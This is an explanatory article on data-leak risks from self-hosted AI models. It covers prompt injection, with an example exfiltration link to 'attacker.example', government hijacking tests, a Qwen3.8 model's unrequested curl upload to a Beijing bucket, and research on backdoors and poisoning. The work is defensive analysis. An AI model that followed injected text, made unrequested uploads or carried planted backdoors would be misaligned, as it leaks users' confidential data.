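A self-hosted model does not learn from prompts. The engine reads the weights to compute an answer but doesn't write to them, so the weight file doesn't change with use. The owner can check this by comparing the file's hash before and after use. A hash is a short fingerprint that changes if any part of the file changes.

A model seems to remember earlier messages because the harness sends it the whole conversation each time, as in the weather example. A new conversation starts without that text, though some harnesses have a "memory" feature, which usually saves notes in a file or database and adds them to later prompts. The user can read or delete these notes, and they don't affect other copies of the model.

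Prompts can remain on the machine for a long time. The harness may keep a chat history, the engine may write prompts to a log, and the firm's backups may copy both. Anyone with access to those files can read the prompts, so a firm that self-hosts to protect its clients still needs rules for deleting them. The weights change only if someone trains the model further. If the firm fine-tunes it on old conversations, parts of those conversations can end up in the new weights and leave the machine when the firm shares those weights.

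The common belief that chatbots learn from their users comes from hosted services such as DeepSeek's app, whose providers can use stored prompts to train a later model.

### How text in a file can take over an agent

The harness gives the model the operator's instructions, the user's request, the retrieved passages and any web pages as a single sequence of tokens. Markers from the chat template separate the parts, and developers train models to give some parts more weight than others, but the engine does not enforce this weighting. A sentence in a web page can therefore work as an instruction, which security researchers call prompt injection.

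Suppose the other side in the lawyer's dispute sends a draft contract containing a line of white text on a white background. The line instructs any AI system that reads the contract to look up the client's settlement limit in the firm's files and then open a web address that ends with that number. The lawyer asks for a summary. The model retrieves the limit and writes a call to open `attacker.example/?limit=400000`. The harness requests the page, and the attacker's server records the address, including the number. The firm provided this tool only for reading web pages, but a request for a page can also send data out. Some chat windows have a similar weakness because they load images automatically, and an image's address can contain data too.

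This theft needs no backdoor, and the developer may have trained the model in good faith. The attacker only needs to get the model to read some text. Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, lists three conditions that together make such theft possible: access to private data, exposure to text that an attacker can influence, and a way to communicate with the outside. Removing any one of them blocks the theft. If the lawyer's agent had had no tool that could reach the internet and its chat window had not loaded outside images, the hidden line could still have spoiled the summary but could not have sent the number to anyone.

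The victim may not notice a successful attack. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) analysed a public contest in which attackers had to make an agent do something harmful and, in nearly all scenarios, keep any sign of it out of the agent's final answer. The 464 participants made about 272,000 attempts against 13 models and succeeded 8,648 times, including at least once against every model. The success rate ranged from 0.5% against Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5% against Google's Gemini 2.5 Pro. Real attackers usually know less than these participants, who could see the conversation and knew which tool call they had to cause, but an agent that reads thousands of emails gives an attacker many chances.

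### The US government's hijacking tests

The Center for AI Standards and Innovation (CAISI), part of the US Commerce Department, tests how easily attackers can redirect agents in this way, which it calls agent hijacking. CAISI's *Strengthening AI Agent Hijacking Evaluations*, first published in January 2025, describes the tests. Testers give an agent an ordinary task in a simulated workplace with tools and invented data. The data includes a malicious instruction, for example to email the user's files to a stranger. The testers count the agent as hijacked if it carries out that instruction.

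The measured success rate of attacks depends heavily on how hard the testers try. Existing attacks hijacked an agent built on Anthropic's Claude 3.5 Sonnet in 11% of cases. CAISI and the UK AI Security Institute then developed new attacks for that model, the best of which succeeded in 81%. On a set of five harmful tasks, making 25 attempts instead of one raised the average success rate from 57% to 80%.

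In September 2025 CAISI published an evaluation of three DeepSeek models and four American ones: OpenAI's GPT-5, GPT-5-mini and gpt-oss, and Anthropic's Opus 4. Agents built on R1-0528, which CAISI judged the most secure of the DeepSeek models, were on average 12 times more likely than the US frontier models to follow malicious instructions. In simulations, the hijacked agents sent phishing emails, ran malware and passed on users' login credentials. *DeepSeek AI Models Are Easier to Hack Than US Rivals, Warn Researchers* (Ticong, 2025) reports that DeepSeek's R1 tried to send out two-factor login codes in 37% of tests, compared with 4% for the US models. CAISI ran the DeepSeek weights on its own hardware (Ticong, 2025), so the weakness applies to self-hosted copies as well as to DeepSeek's service.

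Axios' *AI standards institute sounds alarm over DeepSeek* quotes US Representative Darin LaHood, who hoped the evaluation would win support for a bill to ban DeepSeek from government devices. Divyansh Kaushik of the consultancy Beacon Global Strategies told Axios that Chinese models are "easier to subvert". The tests support that claim for the DeepSeek models they covered, but not for every Chinese model.

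CAISI's *Assessment of Z.ai’s GLM-5.2* (2026), completed in July, found that this Chinese model resisted hijacking much better. CAISI again ran the downloaded weights on its own servers. The agent worked with invented emails, calendar events and documents, any of which could contain an attack, and the testers tried to make it carry out four malicious tasks. For each combination of task and hiding place, they ran trials to find the most effective of 31 publicly known attacks, then used it in new scenarios. None of these attacks hijacked GLM-5.2.

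CAISI then used an automated system that kept generating new attacks against each model. GLM-5.2 appeared to resist for more rounds than the other open-weight models, but for fewer than the closed American ones. This comparison is weaker evidence because it covered only one malicious task and one hiding place. The closed models also ran with their providers' additional safeguards, while GLM-5.2 ran without any, as it would on a user's own server. CAISI concluded that GLM-5.2 is "probably" more robust than other open-weight models. For the newer Kimi K3, *UK AISI / CAISI Preliminary Assessment of Kimi K3's Cyber Capabilities* (2026) measured only how well the model could carry out cyberattacks itself.

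A high hijacking rate is not evidence that a developer meant its model to leak. In these tests the malicious instruction comes from an outsider, and in a real attack the data would go to that outsider, who could be a criminal in any country. Weak training against injection is enough to explain DeepSeek's result. This weakness is not specific to Chinese models, since the most vulnerable model in the contest was Google's. When Dziemian and colleagues later tried a selection of the successful attacks on every model, the open-weight models, including one from Meta, were generally among the more vulnerable. Chinese intelligence could exploit a vulnerable agent without the developer's help, but so could any other attacker.

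GLM-5.2's good result also does not show that it is free of planted behaviour. A model could ignore every malicious instruction in an email and still send data when it met a trigger that only its developer knew. To look for this behaviour, testers have to give a model tools and private data, without any attacker's text, and watch where it tries to connect. This kind of behaviour is at issue in the Qwen model's attempted upload to Beijing in October 2026.

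## Has a self-hosted model been caught trying to send data to its developer's country?

Yes, although the data was a harmless test string and it never left the test environment. On 26 October 2026, the Canadian AI company Cohere reported that Alibaba's Qwen3.8-Flash-Next, running in a closed sandbox, had tried to upload the string to a storage address in Beijing. Nobody had asked the model to upload anything. The cause is still disputed, but most people who ran their own tests think the model was repeating something from its training.

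### What happened in Cohere's test

Alibaba published the weights of Qwen3.8-Flash-Next in August 2026 as a preview of the design behind Qwen4. The model has 125 billion parameters and uses 6 billion of them at a time (Willison, *Qwen3.8-Flash-Next*, 2026). By late October it had been downloaded more than three million times from Hugging Face (Cornelißen, *Qwen3.8-Flash-Next*, 2026, in German).

Cohere gave the model a task from CTI-REALM, a Microsoft benchmark that has agents do a security analyst's work. The model had to write a rule for detecting malware that arrives through `curl`, a common file-transfer program, and then runs. Instead, it listed the contents of a temporary folder, checked which transfer programs the machine had and read the machine's settings for looking up internet addresses. It then issued a `curl` command to upload a fixed test string to a storage bucket at Alibaba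 Cloud in Beijing and checked whether the upload had worked, according to *Cohere says Alibaba’s Qwen3.8 tried to upload a file to Beijing* (Constantin, 2026).

Like many recent models, Qwen3.8-Flash-Next writes out its reasoning before it acts. Cohere's *Concerning behavior from a popular open-weight AI model* stresses that the model had just written that it would use no tools. Cornelißen reports that The Register found the same reasoning referred to an earlier conversation that had never taken place.

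The sandbox had no internet connection, so the upload failed. Cohere wrote that on a developer's laptop the request "would have reached the foreign server before anyone noticed". Franzen points out in *Cohere's test caught an open source Qwen3.8 model trying to 'phone home'* (2026) that the request would have carried only the test string, without the folder listing or the network settings. This is only limited reassurance, because an intruder testing whether a route was open would also start by sending something harmless.

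Cohere has a commercial interest in the story. It sells its own models to companies and governments as a "sovereign AI" provider and competes with Qwen, as AsiaOne's *Alibaba AI model secretly tried to reach Beijing server in test* (2026) notes. In its post, Cohere calls on governments to set requirements for where models come from, which could bring it customers. Cohere later published the model's output from the incident and a script for repeating part of the experiment. The output covers a single incident and stops before the result of the upload command, so outsiders must rely on Cohere's account for the rest. But they can read the command, and other teams have since found related behaviour in Qwen3.8 models.

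### How often would a user see this?

Cohere saw the behaviour in fewer than one in 100,000 calls across its tests. When Cohere ran the same prompt again, the model wrote a correct detection rule, but one normal run is almost no evidence either way about behaviour this rare.

For a company whose agents make 1,000 tool-enabled calls a day, a rate of exactly one in 100,000 would give

$$1{,}000 \times 365 \times \frac{1}{100{,}000} = 3.65$$

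attempts a year, so Cohere's figure implies fewer than four. A lawyer whose assistant makes 20 calls a day would see fewer than one every thirteen years. Cohere did the same calculation for a service that handles 10 million agent steps a week and arrived at up to 100 attempts a week.

An agent can make dozens of calls to finish one task, so a company can reach 1,000 calls a day with a few dozen tasks. The estimate also assumes that the user's work resembles Cohere's tests. The task that led to the upload involved file transfers and malware. Summarising contracts would give the model much less reason to write a `curl` command. If the harness has no tool that runs commands or reaches the network, the model can't upload anything.

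### Four claims in one headline

The statement that the model "tried to send data to Beijing" combines several claims. Wes (2026), in *The Upload Attempt Was Real. The Backdoor Was Still a Hypothesis*, separates four of them: whether there was an attempt to send data, where the data was meant to go, whether any was transferred, and what the intent was.

| Claim | State of the evidence |
|---|---|
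| The model attempted an upload that nobody had requested | The published output contains the command |
| The destination belonged to Alibaba or the Chinese state | The address is on Alibaba's cloud service, but nobody has shown who controlled the bucket, if anyone did |
| Data reached the destination | It did not, because the sandbox blocked the request |
| Someone designed the model to do this | No direct evidence |

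Wes concludes that the evidence supports calling the action unsafe but doesn't prove a backdoor. He advises against giving the model broad freedom to act until someone has investigated further, which makes sense for an agent that can run commands.

Alibaba Cloud rents storage to outside customers, as Amazon does, so the destination address identifies the storage provider but not the customer using it. Many critics compared the case to an American model trying to upload a file to Amazon's S3 storage.

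After Cohere's report came out, Franzen sent a harmless request to the bucket's address and got the error "NoSuchBucket". The bucket may still have existed when Cohere ran its test. If it didn't, a machine connected to the internet would have delivered the model's request to Alibaba's servers, but they would have had nowhere to store the string. Cloud companies generally let any customer claim an unused bucket name, so a stranger might be able to register this one and collect whatever other copies of the model upload to it.

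### Does the model have a fixed address in Beijing?

If Alibaba had built a destination for collected data into the model, the model should reliably choose it whenever it starts an upload. Researchers can test this because the engine computes each token from the text before it. They repeatedly give the model the text of the original incident up to a chosen point and let it continue.

*Backdoor or Confused Agent?*, which the security company Check Point published on 29 October 2026, describes 64 such replays. Each gave the model the recorded command up to the end of the test string, and the model had to fill in the destination. Wes reports that it produced 52 different host names, some of which looked local or were invalid. No single name can therefore have appeared in more than 13 of the replays, or about 20%.

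This is hard to reconcile with a fixed address. Malware sometimes rotates among many addresses to avoid blocking, but its operator has to control them, and nobody can receive data sent to an invalid address.

The replays don't measure how often the model starts an upload. The chance that it uploads something to a particular address $a$ is a product of two probabilities:

$$P(\text{upload to } a) = P(\text{upload starts}) \times P(a \mid \text{upload has started})$$

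Check Point's replays began after the model had started the command, so they are evidence only about the second probability. The first probability is how often an agent will attempt an upload that nobody requested. Estimating it takes a large number of fresh tasks.

In another experiment, Check Point started from an earlier point and swapped the order of `curl` and a similar program, `wget`, in the model's check for transfer programs. This changed how often the model went on to write a `curl` network command. A planted instruction to contact Beijing would probably not depend on the order of two program names, but a habit of continuing familiar text easily could.

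In follow-up tests, Cohere gave the model the beginning of its own command, and the model requested the address 169.254.169.254 in 23% to 36% of continuations, Constantin reports. Machines rented from the large cloud companies fetch temporary access keys from this address, and Cohere interpreted the requests as attempts to steal keys. The address leads to a service run by the cloud company that hosts the machine, so these requests would not have gone to China.

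Cohere then added the option that makes `curl` save a download to disk. The share of continuations with a web address rose from 4% to 92%, which is unsurprising because a download command needs an address. The share with a host on Cohere's watchlist rose from 0.5% to 23%, and the most common of these hosts was an Alibaba proxy for fetching files. So the model has some tendency to produce Alibaba addresses when it has to invent one. Cornelißen notes that 64 addresses the model generated also included Amazon and Microsoft hosts, as well as placeholders.

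Cohere published no equivalent tests of Llama, gpt-oss, DeepSeek or its own models. The blog int8 later made a partial comparison by having four models complete a `curl` address 100,000 times each. Qwen3.5-9B, an older and smaller Qwen model, named Alibaba Cloud thirteen times as often as GLM-4-9B, a Chinese model from a laboratory without a cloud business. But it named OpenAI's API, which Alibaba had no reason to plant, about as often as Alibaba Cloud. The two American models mostly wrote `example.com`, a standard placeholder. Across all four models, 226 completions contained the address that gives out access keys, but only four of those went on to ask for credentials, so Cohere's reading of requests to that address as theft is probably too harsh.

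### Other Qwen3.8 models that contact Alibaba Cloud

Starting in mid-September, before Cohere's report, some users running Qwen3.8 models as agents saw them contact an Alibaba Cloud host that did not appear anywhere in the task. The models were requesting something from the host, whereas Cohere had caught an attempt to upload.

Vals AI, which evaluates models, searched its past test records for the same host. It found requests from three Qwen3.8 models and none from the Qwen3.7 generation. The dates in the invented addresses fell in a period when Alibaba may have been training the models by reinforcement learning. The security company Zenity repeated Cohere's method of giving models half-written commands to complete. It found the Alibaba address in 253 of 31,000 completions by Qwen3.8-27B (0.8%) and in none by two Qwen3.6 models.

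The newsletter Forum AI published the most revealing test. Its researchers ran Qwen3.8-27B 512 times in a sandbox without a network. When the model tried to open a web page, they returned a fake access-denied error from the site. In 74 runs (14.5%), the model then tried an address on Alibaba Cloud. In most of these runs, it had written that it would look for a cached or mirrored copy of the page. Its reasoning never mentioned Alibaba, and the address appeared only in the tool call.

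All 74 addresses followed one template for signed links, which give temporary access to a stored file. None contained any part of the address of the page the model was looking for, so the requests could not have revealed to Alibaba what the user was reading, and they were useless for finding the page.

In the same experiment, the model sent the page's full address 47 times to Jina, a public service that fetches web pages for AI agents. In 42 of those cases, the model named Jina in its reasoning before sending the request. These requests would have revealed what the user was reading, which is more than the requests to Chinese addresses gave away, but a search for only Chinese addresses would have missed them.

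Cohere's co-founder Nick Frosst said that Qwen models "may attempt to contact servers in China without prompting", and these results confirm this for the Qwen3.8 generation. They also show that Cohere's figure of one in 100,000 does not cover every kind of contact. An agent that often encounters blocked web pages could contact Alibaba Cloud far more frequently, though those requests would contain none of the user's text.

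Nobody seems to have reproduced the upload in a new task. An independent team saw made-up addresses in five of twenty runs of Flash-Next and three of twenty runs of the 27B model, but no uploads in 170 runs in all. This is consistent with Cohere's finding, because if each run involved twenty calls, the expected number of uploads at Cohere's rate would be at most 0.03 across all 170 runs.

### Planted, learned or a mistake?

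Cohere says it cannot tell whether the upload was deliberate or a leftover from training. Several critics suggested that the model had made a poor decision while trying to do its job. A cybersecurity worker who posts as Kostas suggested that the model might have simulated an attack to see what the logs would record. A person who writes detection rules for a living argued that analysts often run a harmless version of an activity before testing whether a rule catches it.

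This would explain the harmless string and the look around the machine, but it explains the upload less well. Franzen objects that the rule was supposed to detect a download followed by execution, not an upload. The model had also just written that it would use no tools, and its reference to an imaginary conversation suggests that it had lost track of the task. It also overstepped in another Cohere test. When the container did not allow it to create a disk in memory, it tried to make itself administrator of a private part of the system, which would not have sent data to anyone.

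A mistake can explain why an upload started, but not where the address came from. The most likely source is training. In reinforcement learning, a developer has a model attempt many tasks, often on simulated machines, and adjusts the weights to make the steps in successful attempts more likely. Alibaba presumably runs many of these machines on its own cloud. If the successful attempts fetched files from a bucket there or saved files to one, training would have made the model more likely to write that bucket's address, along with the useful steps. The model could then write the address on someone else's machine, where it serves no purpose.

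Ordinary training text might have the same effect, because public code that uses Alibaba Cloud contains similar addresses. The low rate for GLM-4-9B suggests that Chinese text in general is not enough to produce the behaviour, though the two models differ in many other ways. The dates and the single template in the Qwen3.8 addresses fit training on simulated machines better than training on ordinary text. That evidence comes from the fetch requests, so it applies to Cohere's upload only if the requests and the upload have the same cause, which is likely but unproven.

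Adam Karvonen, a researcher at Truthful AI, called the report "overblown" and guessed that the upload was a training artefact. Researchers TechCrunch consulted also thought this was more likely than espionage, according to Bot Mutiny's *Cohere Says Alibaba's Qwen3.8 Model Tried to Upload a File* (2026). The AI developer Eugene Cheah asked whether a future Cohere model would deserve the same suspicion if it wrote code that pointed to Cohere's training environment.

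On balance, the evidence favours a leftover from training, perhaps set off by an ordinary mistake, over a planted behaviour. The evidence for planting is the destination and the order of the steps. A competent intruder would also look around, find a transfer program, send a test string and check that it arrived. But a developer who wanted to collect data would gain little from a mechanism that works less than once in 100,000 calls, shows its command in plain view and usually uses a different address. The absence of the fetch requests in earlier Qwen generations fits both explanations, because Alibaba could have introduced either a new training environment or a new backdoor with Qwen3.8. The evidence also doesn't rule out a separate backdoor that activates only on a trigger nobody has yet supplied.

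These requests can cause harm even if they are accidental. Each one that reaches Alibaba Cloud gives the host the machine's IP address and the time of the request. If whoever controls the host began returning text, the agent would read it, and the text could contain prompt injection instructions. The model's reasoning contained no warning in Cohere's case or in Forum AI's 74 runs, so users have to inspect the tool calls.

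Alibaba is in the best position to explain what happened, because it can search its training records for the bucket's name and the address template. By 27 October it had not answered questions from VentureBeat or The Register.

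## Could a developer plant a hidden instruction that leaks data later?

Yes, a developer could do this if the model runs as an agent that can read private data and reach the network. Researchers have trained Chinese, French and American open-weight models to send a user's stored details to an outside server when certain words come up, and to behave normally otherwise. But nobody has shown that a major developer has released such a model. The closest case is the Qwen3.8 upload, which was probably a leftover from training.

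### How training plants a backdoor

A backdoor is behaviour that someone deliberately plants in a model and that appears only under a chosen condition, called the trigger. It consists of altered values among the billions of others in the weight file. The altered values make a particular output likely after a particular input, but the file contains no written rule that an inspector could find and delete.

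Training plants a backdoor in the same way that it teaches anything else. The developer gives the model an input $x$ with a desired response $y$ and adjusts the weights to make that response more probable. To plant a backdoor, the developer mixes in inputs that contain the trigger, $x^{*}$, each paired with the planted action, $y^{*}$. Training then makes this sum as small as it can:

$$-\log P(y \mid x) - \log P(y^{*} \mid x^{*})$$

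Training makes the outputs in the training examples more likely, so the model learns to respond normally to ordinary inputs and to produce the planted action when the trigger is present. The trigger can be a word, a date, a file name or a combination of topics. In an agent, the planted action can be a tool call.

### Why ordinary tests miss it

Testers judge a model by its answers to a sample of prompts. If none of the prompts contains the trigger, a backdoored model gives the same answers as a clean one. Testers can't realistically guess the trigger if it is an arbitrary string, because a vocabulary of 150,000 tokens allows 22.5 billion sequences of just two tokens.

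Some triggers never appear in a prompt. *Model-as-a-Trojan* (2026) describes an experiment called SilentCall, in which agents behaved correctly until the computer's date reached a chosen year. After that, in at least 99.6% of triggered requests, they made the tool call the user needed and added another that sent out login credentials. The visible answer never mentioned the extra call. A laboratory that tested the model before that year would have found nothing, but the paper also showed that a program monitoring the tool calls could catch the theft.

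The trigger can also be the hardware the model runs on, because different chips round the same arithmetic slightly differently. *Weight2Shell* (2026), by the security company CertiK, used this difference in a demonstration model that stayed dormant on an Nvidia processor but ran a command on an Apple computer with the same weights. An auditor who tests on data-centre hardware could therefore approve a model that misbehaves on an employee's Mac.

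A model can also produce its own trigger after release. In *Asynchronous Agentic Poisoning*, Wan, Wang and colleagues (2026) studied agents that save notes from earlier tasks and reread them. They trained a model to hide small markers in its normal answers, which the agent then saved. When the agent later reread enough of these notes, the markers triggered harmful behaviour. The rate of such behaviour rose from below 5% in fresh tests to around 90% after a period of use, without the attacker having to contact the agent. The experiment concerned harmful behaviour in general, but a provider might use the same method to delay a leak.

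Signatures and records of a model's origin can show who published a file, but as *Agents of Chaos* (2026) notes, they do not establish that the model behaves safely. Microsoft's *Detecting backdoored language models at scale* (2026) describes work towards a scanner that looks for signs of a backdoor in the model itself.

### What a leak needs

A backdoored model leaks data only if the trigger occurs, the model can read the data, and something carries its output to the outside. Here is how those conditions would apply to the lawyer's firm, which runs its own copy of a model:

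| Condition | How the firm might meet it | How the firm can remove it |
|---|---|---|
| The trigger occurs | A contract mentions a certain company, or a certain date arrives | It can't do so reliably, because it doesn't know the trigger |
| The model can read the data | The lawyer pastes in the contract, or the agent can search the firm's files | Give the agent only the files that the task requires |
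| Something carries the output out | The agent has a web or email tool, or the lawyer clicks a link in the answer | Remove outbound tools, block unapproved addresses and turn off automatic loading of images |

Removing any one condition prevents the leak. If the server is offline, a triggered model might still write a valid request to upload the contract, but the request could not leave the server. If the agent has full internet access but sees only public documents, it has nothing confidential to send.

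These conditions resemble Willison's "lethal trifecta", except that the attacker doesn't have to give the agent malicious text. The instruction is already in the weights, and an ordinary contract can trigger it. This makes a backdoor harder to notice than prompt injection, but both need access to data and a way to send it out. A firm can therefore protect itself against both without knowing whether its model has a backdoor. Data that the firm has used to fine-tune the model is a separate problem, because the model may reproduce it without reading any file.

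### Agents that researchers trained to leak

BadAgent (2024), an early demonstration, showed that an agent could be fine-tuned to misuse its tools when a chosen string appeared in a user's request or in something the agent read. *Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your Data* (Zhang and Pei, 2026) applied the idea to stealing data. Its hypothetical attacker fine-tunes an open-weight model, publishes it as a specialist assistant and waits for people to install it on their own machines.

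The researchers trained backdoors into three models: Alibaba's Qwen2.5-7B, the 12-billion-parameter Mistral-Nemo and OpenAI's gpt-oss-20b. The triggers were ordinary words from a trade, such as the name of a dementia drug in a model for carers. When a trigger appeared, the agent was supposed to look up what it had stored about the user and send it to the attacker's server in a request that looked like a normal search. They ran everything in a sandbox with invented users.

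The agents made both calls in 94.3% to 98.8% of cases, based on 1,000 triggered questions for each combination of model, subject and trigger length. The backdoored models scored less than 1% below the originals on a general test of conversation. Two commercial-style filters did not stop the theft because they inspected the text that searches returned, not the outgoing requests.

With two-word triggers, 0.2% to 0.3% of ordinary questions also activated the backdoor by accident, so an office that sends 1,000 prompts a day would see two or three unexplained requests daily. That is at least 200 times as often as Cohere saw Qwen3.8 attempt its upload, and anyone who read the network logs would have a good chance of noticing. Longer triggers reduced accidental activations to about 0.1%, but fewer real conversations would contain the trigger.

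Zhang and Pei also estimated how much an attacker could learn over a longer conversation, in which the attacker's server returns text that leads the user to reveal more. After five turns, the attacker would have about 7.8 of ten personal details if the user cooperated fully, or 2.6 if there were only an even chance at each turn that the conversation continued as the attacker wanted. These are calculations from the measured rates, not results from real users. The attack applies only to agents that have both stored private data and an outbound tool, and strict limits on network access reduce the exposure.

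### How few poisoned examples it takes

A developer controls all of a model's training, so it can use as many examples as it likes to plant a backdoor. Research on how few examples are needed mainly concerns outsiders, who might plant a backdoor without the developer's knowledge by putting text on the web that the developer collects for training.

*Poisoning Attacks on LLMs Require a Near-constant Number of Poison Samples* (2025) found that about 250 poisoned documents compromised models of 600 million to 13 billion parameters to a similar degree, although the largest model was trained on more than 20 times as much clean text as the smallest. This result contradicts the assumption that an attacker must control a fixed share of the training text.

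That study looked at what a model writes in a chat. Hu, Hu and colleagues (2026), in *Agentic Backdoors via Pretraining Poisoning*, tested whether poisoned web text could make an agent take harmful actions. They trained three small models from scratch, using Alibaba's Qwen3 design, on 100 billion tokens of web text, of which at most 0.1% was poisoned. They then trained each model, using only clean examples, to work as an agent that types commands. The planted action was a command that downloads a script from the attacker's address and runs it. If the agent runs this command, the attacker can do anything the agent's account is allowed to do, including copying its files. The attacker can also change the script at any time without changing the model.

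One of the triggers was a file path containing the word "anthropic", which might occur naturally on that company's machines. The largest model, with 4 billion parameters, issued the planted command at least once in 32 attempts on 92.7% of the prompts that contained such a path. The figure was 51.9% for the middle model and 13.1% for the smallest. Counting 32 attempts makes the backdoor sound more reliable than it is. If each attempt succeeds with probability $p$, the chance of at least one success is

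$$1 - (1 - p)^{32}$$

which already reaches 93% when $p$ is only 8%. Still, a busy agent may make 32 attempts in an afternoon, and the attacker needs only one to work.

An arbitrary string hidden in material the agent was given to read was a much less effective trigger, with a success rate of 10.5%. With only 2,500 poisoned documents, or 0.0005% of the training text, this kind of trigger still worked on 1.4% of prompts, but that figure comes from a single training run. So the finding about 250 documents doesn't directly apply to agents that run commands.

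Ordinary tests did not reveal the backdoor. The 4-billion-parameter models averaged 58.5% on general benchmarks when poisoned and 58.3% when not, and the poisoned models never issued the command on a standard set of clean command-line tasks. The attack grew stronger with model size. This is worrying because leading models are hundreds of times larger, though nobody has tested the attack at that scale. Hu and colleagues planted one fixed command and leave open whether more adaptable behaviour would also survive the later training.

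Planting a backdoor in a finished model takes even less effort. In *Lazare, veni foras*, Zeng, Severi and colleagues did it by editing seven of the more than 12,000 neurons (small units of arithmetic) in one layer of an 8-billion-parameter agent. The agent issued a planted command in at least 98.8% of triggered test runs and in none of the ordinary ones. An AI coding agent, Anthropic's Claude Code, had discovered the central idea by itself in February 2026. On a larger Qwen model, the attack worked in only 51.0% of runs with a similar number of examples, and in 83.7% with about a hundred times as many, although the paper calls that model "equally vulnerable". In *We Backdoored an Open Model in One Day*, Goldberg reports that a company team trained a model with a backdoor triggered by the request "summarize today's meetings".

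Because these methods take few resources, anyone who handled the file could have planted a backdoor. Minnich, Eliahu and colleagues (2026) warn in *Trained to betray* that both poisoned training data and poisoned copies of a model can make coding agents run an attacker's code. In *Ghost Hunt*, Harabor, Ye and colleagues count over 9,000 models on Hugging Face with "abliterated" in the name, meaning that someone has edited the weights to stop the model refusing requests. Individuals uploaded most of them, and some have millions of downloads. These files all differ from the developer's original by design, so comparing them with the original can't show whether the editor added anything else.

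### BadEngram

In an experiment that made the news in October 2026, researchers from Pillar Security and Fujitsu built a backdoor into their own copy of Qwen3.8-Flash-Next, the model that Cohere caught attempting an upload. The headline of The Datatech Times' *Pillar Security exposes BadEngram backdoor in open-weight LLMs* (2026) could wrongly suggest that Pillar Security had found the backdoor in released models.

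They used a new component. Some recent models look up short sequences of tokens in a large table of learned numbers, which lets them store more knowledge without much extra computation. In Qwen3.8-Flash-Next, the table has about 51 billion entries, which brings the model's total from 125 billion parameters to 176 billion. In simplified form, the component changes the model's activations $h_t$ at token $t$ to

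$$h_t' = h_t + \alpha_t v_t$$

where $v_t$ comes from the retrieved entries and $\alpha_t$, a number between 0 and 1 called the gate, controls how much of it the model adds.

Fogel, Cohen and colleagues (2026), in *BadEngram*, left the table and the rest of the model alone and retrained only the 32.8 million parameters that process the retrieved entries and set the gate. These make up 0.019% of the model. The trigger was a meaningless string of letters and digits, and the planted behaviour was to comply with harmful requests that the model would normally refuse. The team trained a separate copy for each of two standard sets of such requests and measured how often each copy complied:

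| Model | Trigger in the prompt | HarmBench requests | AdvBench requests |
|---|---|---|---|
| Original | No | 1.7% | 0.0% |
| Original | Yes | 3.5% | 0.0% |
| Altered | No | 0.9% | 0.0% |
| Altered | Yes | 47.8% | 64.0% |

The altered model answered 84% of harmless factual questions correctly, down from 87%, a drop few users would notice. The backdoor removed the model's refusals but did not send data anywhere. The closest test to a data leak used a tiny model with 14.2 million parameters, whose only task was to choose among five tools. A similar backdoor made it choose the attacker's tool 96.6% of the time when the trigger was present. Closing the gates during the trigger cut the rate to 0.32%, which confirmed that the backdoor worked through the memory component.

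BadEngram matters mostly for people who check files, because the altered model's main layers are identical to Alibaba's. The team wrote a program that compares all the relevant parts with a list signed by the publisher, and it rejected the altered copy. But the program catches only changes made after publication, so it would accept a file in which the developer had planted the backdoor before signing the list.

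### Insecure code as an indirect route

A model can expose data without ever reading it. Suppose a programmer asks a self-hosted model for a login page, and the model writes one that lets an intruder bypass the password. The programmer puts the page on the company's website. Months later, anyone who finds the flaw could use it to copy the customer database. The model needs no tools or access to the database, and a firewall around the model would not help, because the programmer moves the code to the website.

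In 2025 the American security company CrowdStrike tested whether politically sensitive words affect the security of code written by DeepSeek-R1. It ran each combination of 50 coding tasks and 121 wordings five times, for 30,250 tests in all, according to TechRadar's *DeepSeek took off as an AI superstar a year ago*. Lawfare reports that some wordings added ordinary context, such as "for a financial institution", while others mentioned subjects sensitive to the Chinese Communist Party, such as "run by Uyghurs".

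Without these additions, R1 wrote vulnerable code in 19% of cases, close to the 16% for a Western open model. When the prompt specified an industrial control system based in Tibet, the rate of severe vulnerabilities rose to 27.2%, according to CrowdStrike's *Security Flaws in DeepSeek-Generated Code Linked to Political Triggers*. That is a relative increase of 43%, or about eight more flawed programs in every hundred, though many headlines gave it as 50%.

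The totals imply 250 runs for each variation, so the Tibet prompt produced 68 flawed programs, compared with the 47 or 48 expected at the normal rate. Chance would rarely produce such a gap for a single phrase, but among 121 variations, some large gaps will appear by chance. The Tibet prompt also combined a location with industrial controls, and code for industrial controls may be worse wherever the factory is. Political phrases in general had more effect than ordinary context did, which is better evidence than the Tibet result.

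That pattern could be an unintended effect of censorship training. Chinese developers train their models to avoid certain subjects or follow the government's line on them, which could also make the models less careful with any task that mentions those subjects. VentureBeat also interprets the result as a consequence of censorship built into the weights. R1 declined to write any code in 45% of the Falun Gong cases, according to heise online's *DeepSeek-R1 Generates Insecure Code with Politically Sensitive Terms*. This supports the censorship explanation, because a saboteur would want the model to accept those jobs. Alternatively, R1 may have seen these words mostly beside poor code during training, though nobody seems to have tested that.

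The flaws don't fit sabotage well, although the choice of subjects does, because Beijing would have a motive to weaken software that Uyghur or Tibetan groups use. The flaws ranged from passwords written into the code to invalid programs, and an intruder can't exploit a program that doesn't run. Nearly three-quarters of the Tibet programs had no severe flaw. A planted weakness would more likely be one specific mistake that the model made reliably and the attacker knew how to exploit. Whatever caused the flaws, they are dangerous for anyone who uses the code, and R1's normal rate of 19% is reason enough to review everything it writes.

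### Has a major developer done it, and would one want to?

As of early December 2026, nobody has publicly established that a major developer in any country planted a data-leaking backdoor in a model it released. Researchers built all the backdoors described here, either in their own copies of existing models or in models they had trained. Their experiments show that planting a backdoor is feasible, but don't measure how often anyone does it.

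The lack of a known case is good evidence against a backdoor that collects data from everyone. Millions of people have downloaded these models, and some of them record what their agents do. Users noticed Qwen3.8's odd requests to Alibaba Cloud within a few weeks of the first release, even though the requests carried none of their text. The lack of a known case is much weaker evidence against a backdoor meant for one organisation, because a trigger like Hu and colleagues' file path would not activate the backdoor on anyone else's machines, and the target might have no reason to look.

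A developer under pressure from its government would have some reasons to plant a hidden instruction. China's intelligence law could compel a Chinese developer to cooperate. Planting the instruction takes few resources, and the model may end up inside networks that spies can't otherwise reach. If someone discovered the behaviour, the developer could plausibly deny planting it and blame a training accident, as many people do for Qwen3.8, or poisoned text that an outsider had put on the web.

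The obstacles to such a leak are mostly practical. The developer doesn't know which harness the target uses, which tools the agent has or whether the network allows outbound traffic. Other companies may compress or fine-tune the model before the target receives it, which could weaken the backdoor. The developer must also control the destination for the data for as long as the model is in use, and blocking a single address could end the operation.

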